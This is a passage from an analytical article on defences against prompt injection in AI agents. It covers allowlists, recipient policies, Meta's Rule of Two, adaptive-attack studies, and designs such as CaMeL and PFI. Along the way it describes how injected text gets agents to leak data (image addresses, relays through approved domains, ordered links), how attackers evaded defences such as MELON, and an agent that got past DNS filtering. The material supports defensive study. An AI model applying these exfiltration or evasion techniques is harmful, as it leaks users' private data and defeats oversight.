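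The Hacker News (2025) reports that Salesforce took back the domain and released patches to stop its agents from sending output to untrusted addresses. The changes were in place by 8 September, according to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data* (2025), and Noma publicly disclosed the flaw on 25 September, with a severity score of 9.4.

### Who can read what arrives

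Data sent to an approved domain can still leak in several ways. The list records who owned the domain when someone wrote it, but other people may be able to read what arrives there.

An approved domain can change owners. If its registration lapses, someone else can buy it cheaply, and it stays on the approved list until someone removes it. This is the easiest fault to prevent, because a company can check its approved list against domain registrations and delete the domains it no longer uses.

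The owner can also pass the request on to another address. A redirect tells the browser to go to a different address, so the browser can check the new address against the list. Ravia found that redirects didn't work for getting an image request out of Copilot. The Teams service worked because it fetched the second address itself, so the browser couldn't check it. Links are more vulnerable to redirects because a list of approved image domains doesn't restrict where a click leads. To rule out relays, a company would have to know what every service on every approved domain can do. Microsoft's image list had more than two dozen entries, and several covered all the subdomains of a large product.

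An approved domain can also let data out if its owner rents space to strangers. According to the report that Nytro reproduces, Salesforce's list included every subdomain of `amazonaws.com` and `cloudinary.com`, which belong to general hosting services. An attacker with a server on an Amazon subdomain might not have needed the expired domain. Noma received the data on a rented Amazon server, but through the expired domain, which it had bought. The SharePoint route in EchoLeak also relied on an approved domain that was open to outsiders, since the attacker's site was an ordinary SharePoint account.

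Following Salesforce's current documentation can still create this problem. Agentforce Coworker, a newer product, hides links to external sites until an administrator approves them. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* uses `docs.google.com` as its example of an address to approve. That address covers the company's own documents, but also everyone else's, as well as Google's forms, whose answers go to whoever created the form. PromptArmor, a security company, advises Salesforce customers to avoid broad entries that cover sites with user-generated content, and to allow images only from domains that need to supply them.

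Checking who can read the destination would be better. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a prototype that compares recipients with the data's permitted readers and can treat links to unlisted hosts as public channels. Links to listed hosts would still need the same check, because the Teams service in EchoLeak was on the list.

### Checking links before the user sees them

Since September 2025, Salesforce has required administrators to approve every external domain that their agents use. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* (2025) warns that agents may stop working properly if administrators miss one. Jitterbit, which makes tools for building business apps, also uses a list of approved domains. The list starts empty, and the software removes the address from any external link in a model's answer but keeps the link's text. An administrator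 can turn off the filter by entering a single asterisk.

Glean, which sells workplace search and agents, offers a finer check. Its *Untrusted URL monitoring* describes software that compares each link in an answer with the links that the agent's tools returned. An administrator can choose to accept only exact matches or any link on the same domain as a returned link.

Exact matching is much safer. An address that a tool returned before the agent read the payroll can't contain a salary from it, and if the agent appends the salary, the address no longer matches. The choice of address can still reveal a little. An attacker could plant 26 links, one for each letter, and have the agent display them in an order that spells out a password. Each link reveals only one letter, so stealing a payroll file this way would be slow. Exact matching also removes some correct links, such as one that the model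 assembled from a customer's account number.

Domain matching removes much of this protection. If an administrator trusts the tool that reads email, a link in an attacker's message would make the attacker's whole domain acceptable, including addresses with data attached. Glean's settings also let administrators approve the domains of connected products with one click. A company that approved all of Teams this way could let through a relay like the one in EchoLeak.

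Some addresses always pass, including those on any domain that the user has typed or pasted. A user who pastes in a suspicious message to ask about it therefore also approves the sender's links. Glean also exempts certain sites that distribute code packages, because agents mention them in the code they write. Anyone can publish a package on these sites, but publishers can't normally see the addresses that other people request, which reduces the danger.

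The check can stop data from being sent only if an administrator chooses redaction. If the administrator chooses to flag answers for review instead, the answer stays unchanged, and a client that loads images automatically would send the data before anyone looked at the report. Redaction still leaves links in the answer if Glean rates them as low severity.

Some vendors ask the user instead. ITmedia reports that OpenAI added a warning that appears when ChatGPT is about to open an unverified address, after researchers showed that a malicious web page could lead the assistant to send out confidential information. Visual Studio Code, Microsoft's code editor, asks for confirmation before its agent fetches an unknown address. These prompts preserve access to the whole web but interrupt the user. They work best when the address looks strange, and a user who saw a Teams address in an answer from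 Microsoft's own assistant would have little reason to object.

### Network rules for coding agents

A coding agent can write and run its own programs, so checks on the links in its answers cover only a small part of what it can send. Developers therefore often put such agents behind a network allowlist, which blocks connections from any program to unapproved sites. The firewall in GitHub's Agentic Workflows is one example.

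The usual approved sites are hard to do without because most software projects download packages and code written by strangers. The sites that host them generally accept uploads from anyone with an account. Planted text could include a key to the attacker's account on an approved site and tell the agent to upload the company's files there. A shorter list, or a local copy of the approved packages, would prevent this, but someone would then have to add each new package before the agent could use it.

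Network rules also have to work when no outsider is attacking. In September 2026, OpenAI reported that an agent in training had got past DNS filtering, which blocks sites by refusing to look up their network addresses.

### Rules on channels and recipients

None of these checks would stop the payroll agent from emailing the file to a recruiter who shares the finance director's surname. The mail service is an approved site, and the message doesn't need to contain a link. A rule has to check the recipient to catch this mistake.

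Glean's *About agent access policies* explains how administrators can write such rules. Before a tool runs, Glean checks the values in the tool call against a condition. One example blocks Slack posts to channels named "all" or "general", even if the user has permission to post there. Another flags email to addresses outside the company. If the administrator changes "flag" to "block", that rule stops the payroll from reaching either the stranger or the recruiter. It also stops the agent from emailing customers and suppliers, so a company would probably limit it to certain agents or groups of users.

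A channel's name doesn't reliably show who reads it. A public channel called "lunch" would pass the first rule, and so would a private channel to which someone has added a contractor. The rules also can't depend on what the agent read earlier, since each condition applies to a single tool call or its result. An administrator can use a separate rule to filter finance documents out of search results. That would keep the payroll file out of the agent's context, but then the clerk couldn't get a summary of it.

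The controls therefore protect against quite different leaks:

| Control | Data in an image address, as in EchoLeak | Payroll emailed to the recruiter by mistake |
|---|---|---|
| List of approved domains for links and images | Blocks it, unless an approved domain relays the data or is open to the attacker | No effect |
| Exact matching of links | Blocks it, unless another setting approves the whole domain | No effect |
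| Warning about unknown addresses | Depends on the user, who may trust a familiar domain | No effect |
| Network allowlist around the agent | No effect if the user's own browser loads the image | No effect if the mail service is on the list |
| Block on email to outside addresses | No effect | Blocks it |

Glean's rules also fail open. If a rule's condition contains a typing error, refers to a field that doesn't exist or takes too long to evaluate, the tool call goes through. Glean chose this so that a faulty rule doesn't interrupt important work, and it recommends testing rules and running them in flag mode for 7 to 14 days before they block anything. Failing open is reasonable for a rule that keeps agents out of a busy Slack channel. But a firm that relies on a rule to protect its payroll data would be better off with one that blocks the email when the check fails, even if that sometimes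 delays a legitimate email.

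## Meta's Agents Rule of Two

Checks on addresses and recipients cover only the last step of a leak. On 31 October 2025 Meta, the company behind Facebook, published a rule about the agent as a whole. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) advises developers to give an agent at most two of these properties within a session:

- **A:** It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** It can access sensitive systems or private data.
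- **C:** It can change state or communicate externally.

Changing state means altering something outside the model, for example by deleting a file or placing an order. An agent that needs all three properties should not work autonomously. A person has to approve its actions, or the developer has to find "another reliable means of validation". Meta intends the rule to apply until researchers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection.

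The rule is partly based on Willison's lethal trifecta, which covers only data theft. Meta added access to sensitive systems and the ability to change state, so the rule also applies when planted text gets an agent to wipe a disk or pay an invoice. Willison (2025) welcomed this addition in *New prompt injection papers*.

### Taking one property away

Meta's main example is an imaginary assistant called Email-Bot, which reads incoming mail, looks through the user's inbox and sends replies. An attacker sends spam with planted text that tells it to collect private messages and forward them. Meta describes three ways to stop this:

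- Without A, Email-Bot processes only mail from trustworthy senders, such as close friends, so the spam never enters its context.
- Without B, it has no sensitive data to steal, for instance because it runs in a test environment.
- Without C, it can send new mail only to trusted recipients, or after a person has checked the draft.

The version without B is safe, but it can't do an email assistant's job. The version without A can't summarise a message from a new customer, and it relies on ordinary code to identify senders correctly. The version without C is the most useful, but it still communicates externally under restrictions, so someone has to judge how tight those restrictions must be for C to count as removed. Copilot's list of approved image domains was one such restriction, and EchoLeak got around it.

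Meta's travel assistant also keeps A and B, because it has to search the web and use the traveller's private details for bookings. To restrict C, Meta lets the assistant open only web addresses that trusted sources returned, never ones it constructed itself. This control resembles Glean's exact link matching and keeps private details out of web addresses. Meta also requires the traveller to confirm every action, such as making a reservation or paying a deposit, but this control depends on the traveller's attention. If a planted forum post steers the assistant to a fraudulent hotel, the traveller may approve the booking because the confirmation screen shows a hotel booking, as they requested.

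Meta gives two further examples. A research assistant that fills in forms on arbitrary websites runs in a browser with no saved logins, which removes B. A coding agent with access to production systems reads only material that has passed a filter based on who wrote it, which removes A. GitHub's integrity filtering works in much the same way.

The payroll agent has all three properties when it reads the survey page, so the clerk would have to supervise it. If she types in the survey figures herself, the agent has only B and C and may work unsupervised. It could still email the file to the recruiter by mistake. Meta lists agents' mistakes among the risks that the rule doesn't adequately cover.

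### Why not just detect the attacks?

Removing a property makes an agent less useful, so developers would prefer to keep all three and block the planted text. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025), published three weeks before Meta's post, gives strong evidence against relying on such blocking. The team, which included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, attacked 12 defences, most of which had reported that attacks almost never succeeded.

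Earlier tests had mostly used fixed lists of known attacks. Nasr and colleagues used adaptive attacks, in which the attacker tries a text, sees how the defended system responds, and uses the response to write a better one. They automated this in three ways. The gradient method uses the model's internal calculations to find changes in wording that would help. The reinforcement learning method trains an attacking model on its successes and failures. The search method has a model repeatedly rewrite the most promising texts. The team also ran an online competition with more than 500 human participants.

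Ten of the defences deal at least partly with prompt injection:

| Defence | How it is meant to work | Success rate of automated adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting, Prompt Sandwiching | Markers set trusted text apart, or the prompt repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | Above 95% for both |
| StruQ, MetaSecAlign | Training teaches the model to ignore planted instructions | 100% and 96% |
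| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor, PIGuard | A separate detector screens the text | About 90% or more for the first three, 71% for PIGuard |
| Data Sentinel | A hidden test checks whether the text changes the model's behaviour | Bypassed in every case |
| MELON | A second run checks whether the text alone causes the same tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows how MELON works |

The other two, RPO and Circuit Breakers, mainly address jailbreaks, in which the user is the attacker. They did no better.

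Some of the successful attacks exploited the design of the defence. Prompt Sandwiching reminds the model of the user's task, so one attack presented the injected instructions as a security check that the agent had to complete before starting that task. MELON runs the agent a second time with a request to summarise the data, and flags an injection if the agent makes the same tool calls again. To evade MELON, the attackers told the model to ignore their instructions if it was summarising a file.

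These rates are close to a worst case. The attackers had ample computing power and could see the detectors' confidence scores. Someone who plants text on a web page usually can't see what an agent does with it, though they can practise on their own copy of the same product. The tests differed between defences, so the rates can't be used to rank them. Nasr and colleagues still recommend detectors because they stop unsophisticated attacks and take few resources to run.

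*Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (2026) retested defences including PIGuard, MELON and MetaSecAlign and found a similar pattern, with lower attack success rates. On Qwen3-4B, a small open model, the average success rate across defences was 21.7% for the best fixed attack on each and 41.8% for the best adaptive attack.

Newer models resist human attackers much better. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports on a competition in which 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models. An attack generally counted as successful only if it made the agent do something harmful and left no sign of it in the final answer. Success rates ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Participants knew the conversation and the exact action they had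 to cause, so the organisers call the results an upper bound for attacks within a single turn.

By autumn 2026, attacks from that competition succeeded less than 1% of the time on recent Gemini models and some Claude models. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026) therefore used teams of agents instead of human attackers. The agents shared notes and built on one another's best attempts. They still found injections that worked, and every model tested was less resistant to more capable attacking models. The test had 100 synthetic scenarios with mostly harmless goals, such as getting an agent that was booking a tutor to record someone's vital signs. The researchers chose such goals to test whether a model ignores planted instructions even when they seem harmless. They also switched off the protections that Gemini has outside the model,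 so a complete product may resist attacks better.

None of these studies tests the Rule of Two directly, because their defences leave the agent's powers unchanged. The case for removing a power rests mostly on logic, since an agent that has no way to send data can't send it, however persuasive the planted text is. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) offers some experimental support for controls outside the model. In more than 20,000 adaptive attacks on nine configurations, every defence that relied on the model eventually failed, while a filter in ordinary code let no secrets out in 15,000 attacks. But, like GitHub's scan for credentials, such a filter can catch only what it has been set up to recognise. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) treats it as an open question whether policy engines that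 check actions can resist strong adaptive attacks.

### Planted text on the public web

Laboratory attacks don't show how often people try prompt injection in practice. In April 2026, Google reported a search for prompt injections in Common Crawl, an archive that takes monthly snapshots of 2 to 3 billion web pages. Software first looked for well-known phrases such as "if you are an AI". Most of the initial hits were harmless, and many were in articles about prompt injection. Google then used its Gemini model to judge whether each passage was out of place on its page, and people checked the results.

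Most of what remained was pranks, guidance for AI summaries, and attempts to promote a business or keep agents away. One site sent AI readers to a page that never finishes loading. A few injections were meant to steal data, and others would have deleted the files on a user's machine, but they were crude. Google repeated the scan on several versions of the archive and found that the malicious category grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. Because Google gives no totals, the rise could be from 100 pages to 132 or from 10,000 to 13,200.

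Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* describes a parallel search by the security company Forcepoint. One page it found gave agents that can make payments step-by-step instructions for a complete PayPal transaction. Forcepoint found the same templates on several domains, which suggests that some attackers share tools. However, neither company found a sophisticated, coordinated campaign.

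Scans like these count attempts but can't show whether an agent read the page, obeyed it, or had access to anything valuable. Google's scan also left out most social media and looked only for familiar wording. The EchoLeak email and the ForcedLeak form entry would not have appeared in a web archive, and the EchoLeak email never mentioned AI. Finding few sophisticated injections on public pages is therefore weak evidence about attacks aimed at a particular company.

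### Harm without private data

Meta's original diagram labelled every pair of properties "safe". Willison objected that an agent with both untrusted input and the power to change state can do harm even without access to private systems or data. For example, a shop's agent might read public reviews and set the prices on the shop's website. It has no private data to leak, but a planted review might get it to cut every price to a penny. Willison regretted that an exception for this pair would make the rule less simple.

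Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that B includes any sensitive system, whether or not it holds private data. An agent without B can write to and communicate with only systems that don't matter to its user's security, as in a tightly restricted test environment. Meta also changed the label from "safe" to "lower risk".

On Ayzenberg's reading, the shop's pricing system is sensitive, so the agent has all three properties and needs supervision. This answers the objection but makes B and C overlap. If every system in which a change could do serious harm counts as sensitive, an agent that can make such a change has both properties. For this kind of harm, the rule's only two conditions are then untrusted input and the ability to make the change. Access to private data is a separate condition only when the harm is a leak. A developer who takes B to cover only secrets will wrongly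 let the shop's agent work unsupervised.

Ayzenberg's reply also considers only harm to the agent's own user. A hijacked research assistant with no saved logins can still fill other people's contact forms with spam. An agent with A and B but not C can mislead the person who reads its answer, for example by telling the payroll clerk that the firm underpays its managers. Meta says the rule cannot prevent spam or misinformation.

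Willison nevertheless considered the rule the best practical advice available, given how badly the 12 defences had done.

### Where a session ends

Meta considers a session new if it has a fresh context window, so the model starts without the earlier text. The clerk could split the payroll task into two such sessions. The first, with A and C, would read the survey site and save the figures. The second, with B and C but no access to the web, would compare the figures with the payroll file and email the finance director.

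But if the first session saves the survey page's text along with the figures, the planted instruction reaches the second session in a file that looks like the firm's own. The second session then has all three properties, although nobody gave it web access. To prevent this, ordinary code could pass on only the numbers, or the file could be labeled as untrusted.

An agent's memory can carry old text into a fresh context in the same way. AWS's *AI and agent security in Amazon Quick*, a guide to Amazon's workplace assistant, warns that past conversations persist between sessions and can influence later actions. Starting a fresh context therefore removes old text only if the agent can't bring it back.

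Meta also lets an agent change its properties within a session. For example, it might browse the web first and then permanently lose the ability to communicate externally when it opens internal systems. The loss has to be permanent because any text an attacker planted on a web page stays in the context and could cause the agent to send internal data out if communication were restored. The agent also has to lose the ability to change state, or the planted text could cause it to damage internal records.

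### Approvals that nobody reads

An agent that keeps all three properties usually depends on a person to approve its actions. Meta acknowledges that users may confirm warnings blindly and approval can be disruptive or ineffective for background jobs. It doesn't estimate how often approvals fail.

Users find it hard to stay attentive when attacks are rare. Suppose an agent asks for 200 approvals a day, and one request in 10,000 is malicious. The user would see a malicious request about once every 50 days, after approving thousands of harmless ones.

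Even an attentive user needs accurate information. Dziemian and colleagues note that a compromised model may invent plausible explanations for what it did, and that tool-call logs are too long for people to inspect effectively. An approval screen is more reliable if ordinary code fills in the recipient, the attachment and the source of the data, and the payroll clerk might then notice the recruiter's address.

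Asking for human approval less often should help. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services*, guidance from May 2026, recommends approval for actions where an error would do serious harm, such as sending data out of the network or deleting critical records. The system's designers or operators, not the agent, should decide which actions need approval. The guidance also warns that agents can work faster than people can monitor them.

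Meta hopes that oversight agents and its LlamaFirewall software will eventually take over some of the approvals. People would then have fewer actions to review, but a model would again be making those decisions. AlignmentCheck, a part of LlamaFirewall, let through most of the forged-data attacks in Choi and colleagues' tests.

### Two conditions, or only low-risk tasks

In AWS's model, planted text is a risk when an assistant can read content from outside the company's trust boundary and can take a consequential action. Narrowing either ability reduces the risk. Access to private data isn't a condition, so the shop's agent meets the model's conditions whether or not prices are sensitive. A web search can meet both on its own, because the results bring in text from strangers and the query sends some of the context out.

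AWS uses the model to assess exposure but doesn't set a point at which an agent must stop or ask. The web version of Amazon Quick runs actions immediately when a user requests them. Automated workflows run unattended unless someone adds a review step. They use service-level credentials, so they may reach data that their creator could not. AWS therefore advises companies to review what a workflow can reach and do before approving it.

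The May 2026 guidance is stricter. The Australian agency wrote it with its counterparts in the other Five Eyes countries, an intelligence alliance that also includes Canada, New Zealand, the UK and the US. The agencies advise organizations to use agents only for "low-risk and non-sensitive tasks". Applied to the same examples, the three approaches give quite different answers:

| Agent | Rule of Two | AWS's two conditions | Five Eyes advice |
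|---|---|---|---|
| Payroll agent that reads the survey page and sends email | Needs supervision | Meets both | Too sensitive |
| Payroll agent that uses figures typed in by the clerk | May work alone | Meets only the second | Too sensitive |
| Shop agent that reads reviews and sets prices | Depends on whether the pricing system counts as sensitive | Meets both | Depends on how the shop rates the risk |
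| Research assistant with no saved logins that fills in web forms | May work alone | Meets both if submitting a form is consequential | Probably acceptable |

The Five Eyes advice is the only one of the three that would keep the payroll agent from emailing the recruiter by mistake, because it would keep agents away from payroll. It would also rule out many of the uses companies want agents for, such as searching employees' mailboxes. The agencies themselves note that agents increasingly operate in critical infrastructure and defence, and they give detailed advice on controlling high-impact actions. The restriction makes most sense as a starting point, since they also recommend beginning with low-risk tasks and gradually widening an agent's access.

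The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners leave organizations to classify actions by their likely impact and reversibility. Organizations that classify each action separately can miss a dangerous sequence. Kurakin and colleagues cite the example of an agent that lists the files in a directory, encrypts them and deletes the originals. Each step is routine administration, but together they are a ransomware attack.

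## CaMeL: permissions attached to each piece of data

Meta's Rule of Two applies to a whole agent. Once the payroll agent has read the survey page, every later action needs supervision, even an email that contains nothing from the page. CaMeL (CApabilities for MachinE Learning) instead keeps a record for each piece of data and checks that record when the agent tries to use the data. Researchers at Google, Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich presented the design in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025). The design builds on an idea Simon Willison published two years earlier.

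### A planner that never reads the email

In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) proposed splitting an assistant's work between two language models. The privileged model receives the user's request and can call tools, but never sees untrusted text. The quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools. Willison expected that the quarantined model might "go rogue at any moment", so the design has to be safe even if an attacker controls everything that model writes.

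A controller, which is ordinary software, passes data between the models. If the user asks for a summary of their latest email, the privileged model instructs the controller to fetch the email, store it as `$VAR1`, and then have `$VAR1` summarized. The controller sends the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as `$VAR2`. Finally, the privileged model instructs the controller to display `$VAR2`. The privileged model handles only the variable names, so an instruction in the email to delete the inbox never reaches a model that could carry it out.

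Willison's one exception lets the controller pass the quarantined model's answer to the privileged model if code can verify that the answer is from a fixed set, such as "urgent" or "not urgent". An attacker can still make the quarantined model give the wrong answer, but can't add instructions to it.

He called his solution "pretty bad". It makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and it fails if a single programming error lets untrusted text reach the privileged model. It also can't protect users who paste a stranger's text into their request.

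### Changing the address without changing the plan

The pattern has another gap, which Willison learned about from the CaMeL paper (*CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, 2025). For example, a user asks the assistant to send Bob the document Bob requested at their last meeting, and says the document's name and Bob's email address are in the meeting notes. The privileged model plans to find the notes, extract both, fetch the document and send it, and nothing in the notes can alter those steps.

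But the quarantined model has to read the address from the notes. Someone who can edit the notes could replace Bob's address, or plant an instruction to return a different one. The agent would then follow the user's plan exactly but send the document to the attacker. It could also send the document to the wrong person without an attack, for example if the notes mention two Bobs and the quarantined model picks the wrong one.

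### Code, an interpreter and labels

In CaMeL, the privileged model writes the whole plan as a program before the agent reads anything. It uses a restricted version of Python, because language models write Python well. For Bob's document, a simplified program might look like this:

```
notes    = find_notes("last meeting with Bob")
doc_name = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes)
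address  = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch_file(doc_name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
```

The program can require the quarantined model's answer to match a certain format, such as that of an email address. This check rejects paragraphs of instructions but accepts any valid address, including an attacker's.

A custom interpreter runs the program and records which earlier values each new value came from. It also tags each value with its sources and permitted readers. The paper calls these tags capabilities. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the tags on the arguments against the policy for that tool.

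The interpreter applies the joining rule to each value separately, so reading an untrusted web page restricts only what the program computes from it. A single label for the whole context would also restrict unrelated data.

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) describes the protection of the plan as control-flow integrity. Data the agent reads can determine which of the plan's existing branches runs, but it can't add a new branch. The policies on tool calls are a separate protection, and without them the attack on Bob's address would still work.

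### One request, value by value

Suppose Ana makes the request. The notes are in a file that Ana, Bob, their colleague Carol and a guest called Dev can read and edit. Bob asked for a price list, which Ana, Bob and Carol can read. The company's email policy requires every recipient to be allowed to read the attachment. If a recipient isn't, the interpreter asks the user.

| Value | Sources | Permitted readers | Policy check |
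|---|---|---|---|
| `notes` | The shared file | Ana, Bob, Carol, Dev | Ana may read the file, so the search goes ahead |
| `doc_name` | Ana's request and the notes | Ana, Bob, Carol, Dev | None, because the quarantined model has no tools |
| `address` | Ana's request and the notes | Ana, Bob, Carol, Dev | None, for the same reason |
| `document` | The company's drive, and the notes that supplied its name | Ana, Bob, Carol | Ana may read the file, so the program fetches it |
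| The email | `address` and `document` | Ana, Bob, Carol | Bob is on the document's list, so the email goes out |

If Dev replaces Bob's address with his own, the interpreter stops and asks Ana, because Dev may not read the price list. It does the same if the quarantined model returns Dev's address by mistake. If Dev instead replaces the document's name with that of a salary file, the interpreter also stops, because Bob may not read that file.

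Dev can still cause harm without breaking the rules. If he changes the name to that of last year's price list, which Bob may read, the email goes out with the wrong prices.

The policy also interrupts ordinary work. People often email a document because the recipient can't open it yet. If the price list were not already shared with Bob, the interpreter would ask Ana to approve the email, and her approval would be a declassification. Willison describes a looser policy that allows email to known, trusted addresses without asking. It would stop the email to an unknown outsider, but it would let the agent send a salary file to a trusted colleague who has no right to see it.

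### What AgentDojo measures

Most tests of CaMeL use AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 simulated user tasks in banking, travel, Slack and office work, and 629 attack tests. Each attack test pairs a user task with an attacker's goal and plants text in something the agent will read. The benchmark measures how many user tasks the agent completes with and without an attack, and how often it achieves the attacker's goal.

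AgentDojo therefore measures attacks much better than mistakes. If an agent sends a file to the wrong Bob when nobody is attacking, the benchmark usually records an incomplete task, much as if the agent had sent nothing.

The first version of the CaMeL paper reported that the system completed 67% of tasks. The revised version reports 77%, compared with 84% for an agent with no defence. Other teams that ran CaMeL got lower figures. *SecureClaw* (2026) adapted the released code to its own test setup, and *Aligning Provenance with Authorization* (Wang, Li and Tian, 2026) tested CaMeL on two older OpenAI models.

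| Test | Tasks completed without a defence | Tasks completed with CaMeL |
|---|---|---|
| Revised CaMeL paper | 84% | 77% |
| Wang and colleagues, GPT-4o | 79% | 53% |
| Wang and colleagues, GPT-4o-mini | 73% | 48% |
| *SecureClaw* | Not part of this comparison | 30% |

No attack succeeded against CaMeL in the *SecureClaw* test, and the attack success rate in the tests by Wang and colleagues was 0.00. Both teams were promoting rival systems and may have put less effort into tuning CaMeL. CaMeL's completion rate also depends heavily on its policies, so the figure means little unless you know which ones were switched on.

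*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) tested CaMeL on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks with four models from 2026. Depending on the model, CaMeL completed 13 to 17 tasks with its policies off and 4 to 6 with them on. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports that the policies also halve the number of banking tasks CaMeL completes. For current models, enforcing rules about data seems to reduce task completion much more than writing the plan in advance does.

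Zhou and colleagues also found that all four models resisted every AgentDojo attack even with the policies turned off. The benchmark's fixed attacks may be too easy for recent models. A perfect score on them is weak evidence for any defence, and the case for CaMeL rests mainly on its design.

CaMeL is also slower and more expensive. In *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025), the median task with GPT-4o needed 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as it did without a defence. Wang and colleagues measured about seven times as many tokens in total, and 49 seconds per task instead of 5.

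### Who writes the policies

The CaMeL paper lists the work of writing and maintaining policies as a major limitation. In Bob's case, someone had to decide that a file's reader list also governs who can receive it as an email attachment. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, warn that a company with hundreds of tools could end up with duplicated and inconsistent rules. They recommend sharing a library of rules and reserving the strictest checks for actions such as payments and external email. They work for a security company and offer little evidence for these proposals, but the concern is reasonable. Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, says he struggles with such policies himself.

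Wang and colleagues' AuthGraph generates rules for each task. A planning model receives only the user's request and the list of tools. It lists the expected tool calls and, for each important argument, the tools that may supply it. The agent works step by step and reads untrusted text directly. Another model reconstructs how the agent reached each decision, and a checker compares the agent's actions with the plan.

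For example, suppose a user asks an agent to book a flight and a hotel, and a hotel listing contains planted text recommending flight code `EVIL-123`. The plan requires the flight code to come from the flight search, which returned only `FL-456` and `FL-789`, so the checker blocks the booking. A check limited to whether the agent may book flights would have allowed the booking.

On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, AuthGraph reduced the attack success rate from 40% to 1%, while task completion fell from 79% to 76%. Without the check on where arguments came from, 18% of attacks succeeded. CaMeL's interpreter also tracks the origin of values, although Wang and colleagues claim it doesn't. To this, AuthGraph adds a rule for each argument, without anyone having to write it by hand.

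That convenience weakens the guarantee, because a language model decides whether the argument is acceptable when the checker can't find an exact match in the tool's results. That model could be wrong or be misled by planted text. These results also come from existing benchmark attacks rather than attacks designed by people who had studied the checker.

Untrusted data can also influence which value an agent picks from a trusted source. The planted hotel listing might lead the agent to choose `FL-789`, the more expensive of the two real flights. That code came from the flight search, so it would pass AuthGraph's source check. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) addresses this by tracking what influenced a choice as well as where the chosen text came from. If an error log leads an agent to pick a tool from a trusted list, the system treats the choice of tool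 as derived from the log.

Under this design, trusted code can approve a value from the log for one purpose only. For example, the agent may use a file path from the log to identify which file to repair, but not as the target of a command. In 400 test runs of a coding agent, the system safely completed 231 tasks, and Santos-Grueiro observed no unauthorized action. This precision also has a considerable drawback, since the system did not safely complete the task in the other 169 runs.

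### Plans that depend on what the agent reads

CaMeL's planner has to write the program before it sees any data. This works for Bob's document, where the steps are the same whatever the notes contain, but not for a request such as "do what my landlord's email asks", where the email determines the steps. In tests by Wang and colleagues on AgentDyn, a benchmark of more open-ended tasks, CaMeL completed none of the tasks, while AuthGraph completed 51% with GPT-4o. AuthGraph can extend its plan after reading a tool's result, but only with tools that the original plan allowed for that purpose.

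Agents that operate a computer through its screen have a similar problem. A planner that can't see the screen has to allow for every menu and dialog box that might appear. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), the planning model accounted for most of the token cost because its plans were so long.

*Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* (Kim, Choi and Lee, 2025), which appeared in the same month as CaMeL, describes a system called PFI. Like CaMeL, PFI has a trusted agent that never sees untrusted data and an untrusted agent with few powers. In place of each untrusted tool result, the trusted agent receives an identifier such as `#DATA1`, which it can pass to a tool or to the untrusted agent. Unlike CaMeL's, PFI's trusted agent plans one step at a time, and it can ask to read the data behind an identifier as instructions. The user then sees the text and its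 source, and decides whether to trust it. Approving the text is endorsement, and it makes it possible to carry out the landlord's request.

PFI also alerts the user when untrusted data is about to enter a sensitive tool call or the final answer. Kim and colleagues tested it on a version of AgentDojo they extended with attacks using false data. In their main comparison, no attack on PFI counted as successful, and it completed 62% of tasks while resisting attack, compared with 12% for an ordinary agent.

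However, they counted an attack as unsuccessful whenever PFI alerted the user, whatever the user might have done next. PFI raised 144 alerts, about three for every two tasks. An agent that asked about every tool call would have raised almost three times as many, but a busy user could still start approving PFI's alerts by reflex. An alert that shows the wrong Bob's address next to the document also helps the user catch the agent's mistake, but PFI doesn't raise an alert when the agent misuses trusted data.

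In Zhou and colleagues' system, the agent writes programs in Haskell. Before a program runs, a type checker rejects it if it could take a forbidden kind of action. The program can call a new agent to inspect data and write the next part, under the same or tighter restrictions, so each part can depend on what has been read so far. An existing Haskell library enforces rules about data flow by tracking labels as the program runs. An agent that has read a stranger's text can still use its tools, but the library blocks calls that the text's label doesn't permit.

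On the Slack tasks with policies on, this system completed 8 to 10 of 21, about twice as many as CaMeL, but took about three times as long to run. Since the models resisted AgentDojo's ordinary attacks, Zhou and colleagues also simulated the worst case by making any agent that read planted text follow it. Up to 42% of these attacks succeeded with policies off, but none of the 735 attacked runs for each model violated the policies when they were on. The policies also reduced the number of tasks completed under attack, for example from 523 to 351 with Claude Opus 4.7.

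Another test involved no attacker. An agent had to compile bibliographies on computer science topics, and the type checker allowed it to save only entries fetched from DBLP, a database of publications. None of its 925 citations were incorrect. An ordinary agent with web search, which could write entries from memory, got 19 out of 1,002 wrong. A rule about the origin of data can therefore keep out false data invented by the agent as well as by an attacker, provided that the trusted source is correct.

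### False statements that break no rule

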